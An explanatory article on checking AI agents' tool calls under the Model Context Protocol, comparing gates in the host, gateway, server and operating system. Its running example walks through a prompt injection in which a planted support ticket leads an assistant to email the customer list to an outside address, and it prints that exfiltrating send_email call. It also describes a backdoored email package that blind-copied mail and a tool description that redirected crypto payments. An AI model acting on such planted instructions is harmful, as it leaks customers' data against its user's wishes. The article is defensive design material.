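# Checking AI agents' tool calls before they run: permission gates in the Model Context Protocol

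## How an agent calls a tool through MCP, and where permission comes in

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard for connecting AI applications to outside tools and data. A language model by itself only produces text; to search a database, edit a file or send a message, it needs other software. MCP specifies the format of the messages between the application that runs the model and the programs that do this work. An AI agent is a language model that handles a task by calling such tools one after another and reading each result before it picks the next step. Each call is a structured message that names a tool and gives its arguments, so software along the route can stop and inspect it before the tool runs. This check, called a gate, can allow, refuse, hold or alter the call.

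David Soria Parra and Justin Spahr-Summers created MCP at Anthropic, the developer of the Claude models, and the company released it in November 2024. Anthropic's *Introducing the Model Context Protocol* explains that each new data source had needed its own custom connector, and one protocol could replace them. In December 2025 Anthropic handed MCP to the Agentic AI Foundation, a fund it co-founded with Block and OpenAI under the non-profit Linux Foundation. Anthropic's *Donating the Model Context Protocol and establishing the Agentic AI Foundation* (2025) reported more than 10,000 active public MCP servers and over 97 million monthly downloads of the Python and TypeScript software kits. The maintainers published the current revision on 28 July 2026, and their release post (Model Context Protocol, 2026) reported close to half a billion monthly downloads across the four main kits. The two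 counts cover different sets of kits, and automated builds inflate any download figure, so they indicate growth but not how many people use MCP. The US National Security Agency's *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026) describes MCP as the de facto standard for communication among AI-driven services and warns that its spread has outpaced the development of its security model.

### The parts, and the route of one call

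The host is the application that runs the model and holds the conversation with the user, such as a chat app or a coding tool. It connects to outside programs called MCP servers, which offer tools and carry out calls to them. A server may run on the user's own machine or on the internet. The host contains one MCP client for each server, and the clients send the calls because the model sends no MCP messages itself. Under the design in Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026), the host controls which connections exist, enforces security policy and consent, and keeps the full conversation. Each server receives only the context it needs and cannot see into other servers.

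For example, suppose a support team has an assistant whose host connects to three servers. One offers `read_tickets`, which fetches support tickets; another offers `read_customers`, which fetches the customer list; and the third offers `send_email`. A user asks the assistant to summarise the open tickets and email the summary to her manager. The first tool call runs as follows.

1. Each client sends its server a `tools/list` request. The server replies with a definition of every tool it offers: a name, a description in plain language, and an input schema, which is a formal statement of the arguments the tool takes and their types. For `send_email` the schema might require a recipient, a subject and a body, all of them text.
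2. The host puts these definitions, together with the user's request, into the text that the model reads. The model responds with a proposal: the tool `read_tickets`, with the argument `status` set to `open`.
3. The host passes the proposal to the right client, which wraps it in a `tools/call` message and sends it to the ticket server.
4. The server checks the arguments, queries the ticket system and returns the text of the tickets as a result.
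5. The host adds the result to what the model reads, and the model proposes its next step.

Permissions can apply as early as the tool listing. According to the Model Context Protocol page on tools, a server may use the credentials on the request to list only the tools the caller is permitted to use. A model that never receives the definition of `read_customers` is unlikely to propose calling it. But the assistant may need the customer list for other jobs, in which case the decision has to wait until the model proposes a particular call.

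The best time to decide whether a tool call may run is after the model proposes it and before the server acts on it. When a model writes a `send_email` call, no email is sent until the client transmits the call and the mail server carries it out. Before then, any software along the route can discard the call. Microsoft engineers described the same sequence in an April 2026 post introducing a toolkit for checking MCP calls. They pointed out that it has no built-in check of whether this agent may use this tool, with these arguments, at this time, though MCP leaves room for others to build one.

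Two features of the message flow complicate a gate's job. A server may answer a `tools/call` by asking for more input, such as a missing user name. The client then resends the call with the answers attached and a new message number, so a gate may receive two messages for one intended action, the second containing material that the first did not. MCP has also had no sessions since July 2026 (Model Context Protocol, *Key Changes*, 2026), so a gate that relates a call to earlier calls must keep a record of them by other means.

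When a tool cannot complete a call, perhaps because a date has the wrong format, the server returns a result with an error flag. Clients should show this result to the model so that it can correct the call and retry. A permission gate can return its refusals in the same form. This is useful if the model then tells the user what happened, but less so if it treats the refusal as an obstacle and looks for another tool that does the same thing.

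### A ticket that carries an instruction

Suppose that one of the open tickets comes from an outsider with bad intentions. Below an ordinary complaint it contains a passage, addressed to whatever assistant may be reading, which asks for the customer list to go to an outside address. The model reads this ticket along with all the others. It may ignore the passage. If it follows it, its next proposal is `read_customers`, and after that the mail client prepares this message:

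```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 4,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "send_email",
    "arguments": {
      "to": "records@outside.example",
      "subject": "Customer list",
      "body": "Name, email, phone: ..."
    }
  }
}
```

(A real message also carries a block of metadata with the protocol version and the client's capabilities.)

This call is well formed, since the tool exists and every argument is present and has the right type. The email that the user did want, with the ticket summary for her manager, would have the same method, tool name and fields, with different values. A server that validates its inputs against the schema, as MCP requires, would accept both. To tell them apart, a gate needs something from outside the message: a rule about where customer data may go, a record of what the agent has just read, or knowledge of what the user asked for.

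The attack is a prompt injection, in which someone plants text in content the model reads and the model follows it as an instruction. It works because the user's request, the tool definitions and the tickets all reach the model as text, and nothing reliably separates instructions from content the model should only read. The NSA describes the same failure in chains of agents, where one agent receives another's output and mistakes passive content in it for a prompt. The attacker needs no password or access to the host, only the ability to file a ticket.

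Telling the model in its standing instructions never to send customer data outside the company is an obvious remedy, but not a reliable one. Microsoft tested this kind of protection on 45 adversarial and 15 legitimate prompts, and reported policy violations in 26.67% of the adversarial scenarios. The test was small and internal, and Microsoft was presenting its own alternative, so the exact figure deserves little weight; another model would give a different rate. The case for an outside check doesn't depend on that figure, because an attacker can file a hundred tickets with little effort and needs only one to work. Separate software can refuse a call even when the model hasn't recognised the trick.

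### Who is calling, and what they may do

Computer security has long distinguished authentication from authorization, and a gate might check the `send_email` message for either. Authentication establishes who is making a request, usually through a password, key or token that the caller presents. Authorization determines whether that caller may take the requested action. For example, a bank card and PIN authenticate a customer, and the account's withdrawal limit restricts how much that customer is authorized to withdraw.

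In the support example, both checks can succeed and the customer list can still leave the company. The message comes from the assistant, which is acting for a logged-in user, and the assistant has permission to send email because the user asked it to. But she never gave it permission to send this body to this address. An authorization rule that covers only the tool would allow the call. A narrower rule that limits the assistant's email to addresses inside the company would stop it.

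The NSA reports the same pattern with the MCP server for GitHub, the code-hosting service. Users gave the server's tools blanket access to act on their behalf in both public and private repositories. Malicious or compromised tools could then read sensitive content from a private repository and publish it in a public one without the owner's knowledge, using only the access the owner had granted.

Many deployments address neither question. The authorization rules in the November 2025 revision (Model Context Protocol, 2025) are optional. They apply to servers reached over the web; a server running as a local process should instead take its credentials from its environment. The July 2026 changes tighten several details of the authorization procedure, but the maintainers list no change that makes it compulsory. The NSA found that many implementations omit authentication entirely, and that those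 that include it often don't distinguish permission to read a record from permission to create, change or delete one.

### The gate as a reference monitor

Every gate has two parts, which can run in one program or two: an enforcement point, which stops or forwards the call, and a decision point, which determines whether the call is allowed. In the support example, a proxy in front of the mail server might be the enforcement point, and a policy service the decision point. The proxy holds the `send_email` message and passes the tool name, the recipient and the user's identity to the policy service. The service finds that `outside.example` is not on the list of approved destinations and returns a refusal, so the proxy drops the call. Separating the two parts lets an organisation keep its rules in one place and enforce them in many, but even correct rules can't stop a call that never reaches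 an enforcement point.

*Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), a report for the US Air Force's Electronic Systems Division, addresses the same worry. It describes a reference monitor, which checks each attempt by a program to reach data or devices against what that program's user is allowed to do. The system must invoke the monitor on every access, nobody must be able to tamper with it, and it must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely.

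An MCP gate can fail any of Anderson's requirements. The assistant may have another route to the mail system, such as a tool that runs shell commands, which would let it send an email without making a `send_email` call for the gate to check. The gate may keep its rules in a file that the agent has permission to edit. The requirement that a gate be small enough to verify is harder to reconcile with what people now want from one. A gate that compares the recipient's address with a short list is easy to test exhaustively. A second language model that judges whether the email suits the task may catch cases for which nobody wrote a rule, but no one can verify it in Anderson's sense.

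Saltzer and Schroeder (1975), in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, made the first of these demands a general design principle, complete mediation: "Every access to every object must be checked for authority." For MCP, this rules out a common shortcut, in which the user approves a server on first connecting it and the host allows all its later calls. The NSA notes that a trusted server's capabilities or data access can often change without new approval, and that users often remain unaware of the change. Saltzer and Schroeder also recommended fail-safe defaults, under which access is refused unless a rule permits it. A gate built this way will block some harmless calls that nobody thought to permit, so its owner has to decide whether the protection is worth the interruptions.

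These principles were developed for operating systems in which a program's authority came from the person running it, and they carry over to agents with one important gap. A reference monitor checks whether the caller has the authority for an access, and the assistant exploited by the planted ticket already has it. Perfect mediation guarantees that the `send_email` call reaches the gate, but not that the gate has rules or evidence good enough to refuse it.

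### What MCP requires

The MCP specification gives certain capitalized words fixed meanings, as is common in internet standards. MUST marks an absolute requirement, while SHOULD marks a recommendation that an implementer may set aside for a valid reason after weighing the consequences. These words therefore determine which parts of a permission gate are required and which are only recommended.

According to the Model Context Protocol page on tools, there "SHOULD always be a human in the loop" who can deny tool calls, and applications SHOULD present confirmation prompts for operations. Developers may expose tools through any interface they like. Because human control is recommended rather than required, a host that sends every call without asking anyone does not break an absolute rule.

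The Model Context Protocol overview contains a stronger-sounding sentence, "Hosts must obtain explicit user consent before invoking any tool." But the "must" is in lower case, and the overview makes such key words binding only when they are capitalized, so a developer could fairly read the sentence as a description of good practice. According to the overview, MCP "cannot enforce these security principles at the protocol level", and implementers SHOULD build the consent and authorization flows themselves. This is somewhat reasonable, because one standard has to serve both a hobbyist's weather tool and a bank's payment system, and a compulsory prompt before every call would suit only one of them. But it means a buyer can't tell from a product's MCP support whether the product checks its calls.

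Under MCP, servers MUST validate all tool inputs, implement proper access controls, limit the rate of calls and sanitise their outputs. Clients SHOULD ask for confirmation of sensitive operations, show the user a tool's inputs before sending the call, check results before the model reads them, and keep a log. Showing the inputs is meant to prevent data leaks. In the support example, the user would see the outside address before the email was sent. The mail server must validate its inputs, but it receives only an address and a body, without the conversation that would show them to be unwanted. The host has that conversation, but MCP only recommends that the host check the call. MCP leaves it to the people who build and deploy the system to decide what counts as "proper" access control, who writes the policy and which component applies it.

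## Where the check can sit: host, gateway, server or operating system

A tool call passes through several programs before it has any effect, and a gate can sit in any of them. The host can check the call before its client sends it. A gateway, a proxy between clients and servers, can check it on the way. The MCP server can check it before acting. The operating system can limit which files and network addresses the server's program reaches while it acts. These positions differ in the information available and in who controls them, so a rule that is easy to enforce in one may be impossible to enforce in another.

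### The host has the conversation

A gate in the host has the most context, because it can check the proposed email to `outside.example` against both the user's request and the ticket the model has just read. It can also check calls to tools outside MCP. Many coding assistants, for example, have a built-in tool for shell commands, which are text instructions to the operating system. The host runs these commands itself, so it can refuse them.

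The company that develops the host decides what checks it offers, and the user or her employer chooses the settings. Some hosts also let users or employers add their own checks. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding tool, runs scripts called hooks at set points, such as just before a tool call. But a script written for one host usually won't work in another, so a firm whose staff use five assistants has five gates to maintain.

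The host also tends to run on the same machine as the agent's tools, so the agent can often access the gate's settings. If the host's check crashes or a user switches it off, the host still sends the call with the user's full authority, and the server cannot detect that the check is missing.

### The gateway has the messages

A company with many agents can route their traffic through one gateway and keep its rules there. Uber reports in *Designing MCP Gateway* (2026) that its gateway hosts more than 800 MCP servers and 5,000 tools. The gateway also translates MCP calls into the formats of Uber's existing internal services, so a team can offer a service as a tool without writing an MCP server. *MCP-DPT* (2026), a taxonomy of MCP defences by position, covers gateways that companies can buy, including Lasso Security's, which centralises access rules, and eqtylab's, which adds approval workflows.

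*Mandato* (2026) proposes a gateway that checks an agent's calls against digitally signed mandates. In that design, the email to `outside.example` would go through these steps.

1. The gateway intercepts the call. The host's client connects to the gateway as if it were the mail server, so the gateway receives the whole `tools/call` message.
2. The gateway queries the decision point, passing on the caller's identity, the tool's name and the arguments. The decision point looks up the mandate, checks that nobody has revoked it and counts the call against any quota.
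3. The gateway applies the verdict. It forwards an approved call to the real mail server. If the verdict is a refusal, the mail server receives nothing. Some calls need a person's confirmation, and Mandato parks these as MCP tasks, a mechanism for long-running work, so that the connection needn't stay open while the person decides.
4. The gateway logs the call and the verdict, and later the server's result.

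None of this helps if the agent can connect to the mail server directly. Mandato therefore has the servers accept connections only from the gateway, which proves its identity with a cryptographic certificate. A company can arrange this for servers it runs. It can't expect an outside provider to refuse direct connections, but it can keep the provider's access token in the gateway so that the agent can't log in on its own. Zuplo's *MCP Gateway Public Beta* (2026), a product announcement, describes a feature of this kind. However, an attacker who breaks into the gateway gets the tokens for every server behind it.

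The other main weakness of a gateway is that it receives calls without the conversation. It can read the email's address and body, but not the user's request unless the host attaches it. A gateway therefore works well for blocking outside recipients, which requires only the address, but it needs the user's request to check whether the email suits the task.

### Hiding a tool or refusing a call

Like a server, a gateway can leave tools out of the list that the client receives. WorkOS's *MCP interceptors* (2026), a post by a login software vendor, describes a dispute among developers over whether hiding tools or checking each call better protects against prompt injection. Some prefer hiding tools, because planted text is unlikely to make a model call a tool it hasn't been shown. Others point out that access often depends on the arguments, which don't exist until the model proposes a call.

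In the support example, the assistant needs `send_email` for the manager's summary, so the gateway can't hide that tool and has to check the recipient. If the assistant only ever summarises tickets, it doesn't need `read_customers`, and the gateway can hide that tool without affecting the assistant's work.

Hiding a tool from the list isn't sufficient without a check at call time. A planted ticket might name the hidden tool, and the model might then propose it. *The New MCP Roadmap* (Soria Parra and Delimarsky, 2026) includes cacheable lists among the changes in the July revision, so a client may also still hold a definition that an administrator has since withdrawn. Zuplo claims that its filter covers both cases by omitting hidden tools from the list and blocking direct calls to them before they reach the server.

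*GatewayBench* (2026), which compares seven gateways, describes a hierarchical type in which the agent finds tools through special discovery tools rather than a plain list. A company that uses this type has to filter the discovery results as well.

### When the gate breaks down

When a check produces no verdict, the gate can either refuse the call (fail closed) or let it through (fail open). Mandato's enforcement point fails closed. In *Bounded Agents* (2026), a design for agents that delegate work to one another, the gateway refuses an action if it can't reach the store where it saves evidence of each action.

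Failing closed is more secure because an attacker can overload the decision point of a gate that fails open, then send the email unchecked. WorkOS reports one developer's view that refusal is the only acceptable default. On this view, a system that fails open but keeps logs may be worse than one with no checks, because its records look like compliance.

But failing closed makes every agent depend on one service. *Agentic Architecture of Information Systems. The AAM/5C Model* (2026) points out that even harmless actions stop if the component that authorises them fails, and proposes a set of pre-authorised capabilities to reduce the dependence. A reasonable compromise is to fail open for some actions and closed for others. For example, an agent could keep reading open tickets during a ten-minute outage, which carries little risk, while an email to a new address waits. *ADR-005* (2026), a design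 record for the MCP-checking proxy MCP Hangar, describes a similar plan to replace the proxy's single fail-open or fail-closed setting with a separate setting for each check.

A gate that is working normally can also let calls through because nobody has written a rule for them. *AEGIS* (2026), a system for preventing resource abuse, checks each call's parameters against set limits, using a cache of structured descriptions of known tools. If the cache has no description of a tool, AEGIS treats the call as outside the scope of its policies, so a newly added tool may go unchecked. Uber's software, which scans the company's services for anything that could become a tool, takes the safer approach of registering each new tool as disabled.

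### Interceptors, a proposed standard for attaching checks

Each host and gateway currently has its own way of attaching a check, so M clients and N kinds of checking software may need M × N separate integrations. A common interface would reduce that to M + N. The Model Context Protocol's *Interceptors Charter*, dated 21 April 2026, set up a working group to design such an interface. The proposal is Specification Enhancement Proposal 1763 (SEP-1763).

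An interceptor is checking software that other programs can discover and call through MCP's message format. It can run inside a host or server, beside one as a separate process, or as a remote service. The two types are validators, which pass or fail a message, and mutators, which return a changed version. Each interceptor declares which events it handles, such as `tools/call`, and whether it acts on the request to the tool or the response from it. Model Context Protocol's *MCP Interceptors* (2026), an experimental implementation in Go, includes a validator that rejects every call to a tool named `dangerous_tool`.

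The order in which interceptors run affects how much a validator's approval means. According to *Interceptors for MCP*, slides by two Bloomberg employees (Degiorgio and Chan, 2026), the sender of a message applies mutators, then validators, and then sends it. The receiver runs validators, then mutators, and then processes the message. Validators can run in parallel because they change nothing, while mutators run one after another because each works on the previous one's output. In the version of the draft that WorkOS describes, each mutator has a priority number and the lowest runs first. A validator can attach a warning without blocking the message, but an error rejects it.

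Suppose the assistant's summary for the manager contains customers' phone numbers. Before the email leaves the host, a mutator replaces the numbers with placeholders. A validator then checks the recipient and the redacted text, so it approves the message that the host will send. On the receiving side, a mutator can change the arguments after the validators have approved them, just before the tool runs. That mutator needs as much scrutiny as the gate, because a faulty one could put back a recipient that the validators would have refused.

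Both types of interceptor can run in enforce mode or audit mode. In enforce mode, a failed validation blocks the message and a mutator's change takes effect. In audit mode, a validator records its result without blocking the message, and a mutator computes its change without applying it. A company could run a new recipient rule in audit mode for a week, count how many wanted emails it would have stopped, and only then enforce it. Audit mode replaced a third, observation-only type of interceptor in the original proposal.

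The interceptor proposal is still unfinished. According to MCP Hangar's design record, the original issue was opened in November 2025 and closed on 22 April 2026, and the revised text that replaced it, pull request 2624, was still open on 1 May. In mid-July, WorkOS described the proposal as a draft with no committed protocol version or timeline. In August, Soria Parra and Delimarsky set out five priority areas for MCP, none with interceptors in its title. Some developers already build to the draft, but a product that supports MCP may not be able to run interceptors.

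### The server has the resource

The server, or the system behind it, holds the records that a call concerns. The ticket system stores which customer filed each ticket and which employees may read it. *A Gateway Architecture for Enterprise MCP Authentication* (2026) has the gateway check whether an identity may reach a tool, while the downstream system checks whether that identity may access particular data. The gateway forwards a credential with suitably limited scope, and the ticket system applies its own rules to it. The company therefore doesn't have to copy the permissions for every record into the gateway, where they would soon be out of date. But if the server logs in to the ticket system under one shared account for all users, the ticket system can't distinguish between them.

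A server without access to the conversation can use only blunt rules to check a call's purpose. For example, the mail server could refuse to send to any outside address, but a support team often needs to email customers.

Michael Schwartz, a developer of identity software, objects to relying on the gateway alone. His objection is strong when a company runs its own servers, because the server has facts about the resource that the gateway lacks, and a caller who reaches the server by another route bypasses the gateway's rules. Gateway advocates reply that companies can't alter third-party servers. Mandato's design lists as an advantage that agents and servers don't need to be modified, since an administrator only has to change the address the agents connect to.

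Which side is right depends on who maintains the server. A company should put checks in a ticket server that its own engineers maintain, because these still apply if the gateway fails. With a provider's server, the gateway may be the only place on the route where the company can add its own rule. *Bounded Agents* similarly treats the gateway as an additional layer that doesn't replace the downstream system's own authorization.

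### An approved call can have a different effect

A check on a message can only cover the requested action. The server's code determines what happens, and it may do something else through a bug or by design. For example, a call to `send_email` with the manager's address is a request for one email to one person, but MCP doesn't prevent the server from sending a second.

In September 2025, the security company Koi Security reported a case of this kind. The package `postmark-mcp` let agents send email through the delivery service Postmark, although its author had no connection with the company. Fifteen versions worked as users expected, but version 1.0.16 added a line of code that sent a blind copy of every outgoing email to an address outside the user's control. A gateway in front of this server would have received an ordinary call with the right recipient, because the server added the extra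 one after the check. A confirmation prompt would also have shown only the intended recipient, and the user would have approved it.

*MCP-38* (2026), a taxonomy of threats to MCP systems, notes that such attacks exploit the lack of a built-in way for clients to verify that a tool's description, code and behaviour are the same as when they approved it. It recommends that operators sign their tool descriptions, that clients store hashes of the approved ones (short fingerprints that change whenever the content does), and that changes be logged permanently. Hashing the description would not catch a change to the server's code that leaves the description the same, and a hidden blind copy could easily be added that way. Keeping `postmark-mcp` at an earlier, reviewed version would have protected a company until someone approved the upgrade. With a remote server, the customer usually can't inspect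 the code or choose the version.

### A sandbox limits the effects

A sandbox is a restricted environment in which the operating system controls what a program can reach, regardless of what the program is meant to do. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026) applies one to MCP servers that run on the user's machine. Such a server normally inherits the user's access to files and the network, so a server that looks up places on a map could also read the user's passwords.

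In AgentBound, each server has a manifest that lists the general capabilities it needs, such as reading files or making outgoing connections. AgentBound bases its set of capabilities on Android app permissions, adapted for desktop computers. When the server starts, the user turns each capability into a specific permission, such as read-only access to one folder or connections to one website. The server can't obtain a permission that its manifest doesn't cover.

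A component called AgentBox then runs the server in a container, an isolated environment with its own view of the machine. It gives the server only the approved folders and environment variables, which are settings that often include passwords. It also looks up the network addresses of the approved sites and sets the firewall to block all others. The server's code needs no changes. However, AgentBox installs the server's package before it turns on these network restrictions, so code that runs during installation can still connect to the internet.

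Writing accurate manifests for thousands of servers would take a lot of work, so Bühler and colleagues tested whether language models could do it. They took 296 of the most popular MCP servers, had one model draft five manifests for each from its code and documentation, and had another merge the drafts. In the resulting manifests, 83.1% of the servers needed outgoing network access and 74.1% needed to read files. At least 57% must therefore need both, which could let a malicious server read private files and send them out. General capabilities therefore offer limited protection, so it matters which specific folders and sites a server can access.

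The reported accuracy of the manifests was 80.9%, but this figure is based on few replies. The researchers sent manifests to the developers of 96 servers, and 74% never responded. The reported percentages work out to 17 acceptances and four rejections, with four cases still under discussion. A comparison with manifests that two of the researchers wrote by hand gives better evidence. Across 48 servers, the generated and handwritten versions agreed on 787 of 816 yes-or-no decisions about capabilities, or about 96%. However, most servers need only a few capabilities, so many of those decisions were easy. Of the 48 generated manifests, 20 differed from the handwritten version on at least one capability. Most differences were omissions, which would make the sandbox block something the server needs.

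In security tests, the AgentBox sandbox blocked two of four servers taken from a public collection of malicious behaviours. Both secretly switched to a different network address. AgentBox missed a time-zone server whose tool description contained instructions for the model to redirect cryptocurrency payments made with another tool, and an SQL injection, in which an attacker hides database commands in ordinary input. Both missed attacks used only access that the servers legitimately had. In a separate set of ten deliberately vulnerable servers, AgentBox stopped the attacks on six, partly stopped those on one, and missed those on three. The researchers wrote or checked the manifests for these tests themselves, so an ordinary user who approves permissions without much thought might get weaker protection.

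AgentBox slowed local servers so little that speed is no reason to run them without a sandbox. It added an average of 0.6 milliseconds to each operation on a Mac and 0.29 milliseconds on a Linux machine, plus a few tenths of a second when a server started.

AgentBound would probably not have stopped `postmark-mcp`, though. The server sent its blind copies through Postmark's own service, which it needed to reach for legitimate emails. A firewall rule that allows connections to Postmark also allows the copies, because it checks the destination of the connection and not the recipients of the email. To catch the copies, a company would need to check the outgoing request, either in the email service or in a proxy that can read the server's traffic. A sandbox on the user's machine also can't restrict a remote server, because that server runs on someone else's machine.

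### Routes that an MCP gate doesn't cover

A gate on MCP traffic covers only the actions agents take through MCP. If the host has a shell tool, the assistant could use it to upload the customer list without sending any message through the gateway.

A tool that runs code leaves a similar gap inside MCP. The gateway receives a single call with a script as its argument, and the script can open many network connections. *Bounded Agents* describes its gateway as the single chokepoint for an agent's actions, which the model cannot bypass by producing different text, but this is true only if whoever deploys the agent has closed the other routes.

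Security researchers met the same difficulty with system-call interposition, an older technique in which a tool intercepts a program's requests to the operating system and decides whether to allow each one. Tal Garfinkel's *Traps and Pitfalls* (2003) found that such tools often overlook indirect paths to a resource. For instance, a program that isn't allowed to open a file might receive it already open from another program. The tool can also misjudge a request that the operating system later interprets differently. If the tool approves a request to open a harmless file, and another process replaces that file with a link to a secret one before the operating system opens it, the program gets the secret file. Garfinkel also warned that refusing requests can have side effects, since programs may handle an unexpected refusal badly.

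All three problems also arise in MCP. The shell is an indirect path to the mail system. A gateway that approves a file path relies on the server to interpret the path the same way. Refusals may have worse side effects with agents than with ordinary programs, because an agent may try the shell next to finish its task, even without an attacker.

A company can close many of these routes by blocking all outgoing connections from the agent's machine except those to the gateway and the model. It can also run the shell tool in a sandbox and keep passwords and tokens off the machine. These measures are not part of MCP, but the gateway's rules depend on them.

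The table compares the four positions.

| Position | Evidence available | What it can stop | Who controls it | What happens when it fails |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Host | The conversation, every proposed call and its result, including tools outside MCP | Any tool call before it leaves the host | The host's developer, with settings chosen by the user or employer | Calls leave with the user's full authority |
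| Gateway | MCP messages and the caller's identity | Calls to servers that the agent can reach only through the gateway | The organisation that runs the gateway | If it fails closed, tools behind it stop working; if it fails open, calls go unchecked |
| Server | Its own calls and the records they concern | Access to particular records, mailboxes or accounts | The server's operator, often another company | A faulty or malicious server ignores its own rules |
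| Operating system | Files opened, programs started and network connections made | Effects outside the permissions granted to a local program | Whoever runs the machine | A flaw in the container software lets the program out |

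## What a request tells the gate, and which parts can be trusted

Wherever a gate sits, it has to determine how far it can trust the messages it receives. An authenticated field, such as a valid access token, comes with proof of its source. A checkable field has no such proof, but the gate can compare it with independent information, such as a list of permitted tools. All other fields are merely claimed, because the sender could have written anything in them.

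### One call, field by field

Calls to remote servers travel over HTTP, the protocol that web browsers use. Each call is a separate request, with short headers at the top and the MCP message in the body. Under the July 2026 revision, the email that the planted ticket prompted would arrive like this (with the token shortened):

```http
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
Content-Type: application/json
Accept: application/json, text/event-stream
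Authorization: Bearer eyJhbGci...
MCP-Protocol-Version: 2026-07-28
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: send_email

{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 4,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "send_email",
    "arguments": {
      "to": "records@outside.example",
      "subject": "Customer list",
      "body": "Name, email, phone: ..."
    },
    "_meta": {
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/protocolVersion": "2026-07-28",
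      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientInfo": {
        "name": "SupportAssistant",
        "version": "2.1"
      },
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientCapabilities": {}
    }
  }
}
```

The `Authorization` header holds an access token, which an authorization server, such as the company's login service, issues after the user logs in and agrees to the access. According to the Agentic AI Foundation, the authorization server establishes who the caller is and what access she has granted. The MCP server then checks that the token is valid for that server and that its own policy allows the call. A token usually carries scopes, which are named permissions such as reading tickets. Model Context Protocol (2026) recommends that servers indicate to clients which scopes a request needs, so that clients don't request extra ones.

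The token counts as authenticated only after the server has validated it, which includes checking its audience, the service it was issued for. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* forbids servers to accept tokens issued for other services. Otherwise a token for the company calendar might also give access to the mail server. Even a valid token doesn't prove that the user asked for this email. A server that runs as a local process gets no HTTP headers, so the messages it receives normally contain no authenticated field.

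A gate can check the tool name and the arguments. It can look up `send_email` in its policy and compare `outside.example` with a list of approved domains. But an argument can also contain a claim that the gate can't verify. If the tool had a `reason` field, the model might fill it with "requested by the manager" because of an instruction in the planted ticket. The gate could check that the field contains text, but not whether the manager made the request.

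The `_meta` block holds request metadata. It must include the protocol version and the client's capabilities, or the server must reject the call. The client's name and version are optional. Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) warns that the sender reports these itself, that MCP does not verify them, and that implementations SHOULD NOT rely on them for security decisions. A rule that lets only `SupportAssistant` send email would not stop anyone who knows the name. The name is still useful in a log, as long as readers remember that the sender supplied it.

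| Part of the request | Status | Use to a gate |
|---|---|---|
| Access token | Authenticated, once validated | Identifies the principal and the scopes granted |
| Tool name | Checkable | Comparison with the policy and the server's tool list |
| Arguments | Checkable, except for any reasons or explanations they give | Comparison with the schema and with rules about values |
| Protocol version | Checkable against its copy in the header | Shows which rules the sender claims to follow |
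| Client name and version | Claimed | Display, logging and debugging |
| Client capabilities | Claimed | Choice of optional features |
| `Mcp-Method`, `Mcp-Name`, `Mcp-Param` headers | Checkable against the body | Quick routing and refusal of whole tools |

### Why the headers must match the body

The `Mcp-Method` and `Mcp-Name` headers repeat the method and tool name from the body, so load balancers and gateways don't have to parse every message. Model Context Protocol's release post also promotes letting gateways "route and authorize on headers directly".

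A gateway can safely rely on the header only if it matches the body. A compromised client could put `read_tickets` in the header and `send_email` in the body. A gateway that reads only the header would let the request through, and a server that reads only the body would then send the email. Model Context Protocol's *Streamable HTTP* therefore requires every server that processes the body to compare the two. If they differ, or a required header is missing, the server must reject the request with HTTP status 400 and the MCP error code -32020, `HeaderMismatch`.

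However, the server compares the headers with the body only after the gateway has decided, so the gateway depends on the server to do it. Older revisions of MCP don't require this comparison. A gateway that enforces policy from headers SHOULD check that the version header indicates a revision that requires it, and refuse the request if it doesn't. But the version number doesn't guarantee that the server's developer implemented the comparison. A gateway in front of a server that another company runs should parse the body and compare the copies itself.

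A server can also mark arguments in a tool's input schema so that the client copies them into headers. For example, if the ticket server marks `status`, a call to `read_tickets` could arrive with the header `Mcp-Param-Status: open`. A client that still holds the definition from before the mark was added will leave the header out, and the server will reject the call. The client should then fetch the tool list again and retry. Some mismatches therefore come from an outdated list, and a gateway that raised an alarm at each one would produce many false alarms.

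If a tool name contains characters that are unsafe in a header, the client encodes it in Base64, which represents any text using plain letters, digits and a few symbols. A gateway has to decode the name before checking it against its rules. Otherwise, a forbidden tool could get past a list of forbidden names because its encoded name wouldn't match. A list of permitted names would fail more safely, since the gateway would reject any name that wasn't on it.

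The main problem with reading only headers is that they contain so little. The summary for the manager and the stolen customer list have identical headers, because both are calls to `send_email`. The recipient would appear in a header only if the mail server's developer had marked it. The protocol's guidance is not to mark personal information, because every intermediary can read headers. If the tool takes a list of recipients, the developer can't mark it, because only single strings, whole numbers and true-or-false values can be marked. A gate that reads only headers can block email altogether, but it usually can't distinguish one email from another. It also misses any answers that the client attaches when it resends a call.

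### Keeping records without sessions

Before July 2026, a remote server could give a client a session identifier, which the client sent back with every later call in the `Mcp-Session-Id` header. A gate could use that identifier to group calls into one history. The July revision removed the identifier and the opening exchange in which client and server identified themselves (Model Context Protocol lists both changes). A server built only for the new revision should ignore a session header from an older client.

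The Model Context Protocol overview lets clients mix unrelated requests on one connection and forbids servers to infer a client's identity or capabilities from earlier requests, even if the connection is still open.

The change helps with rules about a single call. The Agentic AI Foundation points out that any proxy or policy engine can now read a request without shared memory. A company can run ten copies of its gateway and send each call to whichever copy is free.

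Rules that depend on several calls become harder to enforce. Suppose a rule forbids email to outside addresses once the assistant has read the customer list. One copy of the gateway handles `read_customers`, then another handles `send_email`, and neither message refers to the other. To enforce the rule, the copies need a shared record and a common key for filing both calls.

The user's identity, taken from the token, is authenticated but doesn't distinguish between her conversations. If she has the customer list open in one, the gate would also block a harmless reply to a customer in another. MCP reserves a metadata field, `traceparent`, for an identifier that links related requests in monitoring software. This could separate the two conversations, but the client chooses the value, so a compromised client could start a new trace just before sending the email. The host knows which conversation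 each call belongs to and could add its own identifier to `_meta`, but the gateway would then have to trust the host.

If a company manages its employees' hosts, the best of these keys is probably the user's identity combined with a conversation identifier from the host. A company that can't trust the host should use the authenticated identity alone and accept more false stops.

Existing gates may also have depended on sessions without anyone noticing. Nwodo and Garg (2026) caution that the change involves more than load balancing and new software kits, because teams can no longer rely on the connection to carry context implicitly. A gate that counted calls per session might count every call as the first after an upgrade.

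### Whose authority a call uses

Sending one email can involve up to three identities: the user who asked for the work, the agent that made the call, and the mail server's own account, if it uses one to send the message. A rule that permits "support staff" to email customers applies to the user, while a rule that bars experimental agents from sending email applies to the agent. The mail system behind the server may have a record of only the server's account, not the user or the agent.

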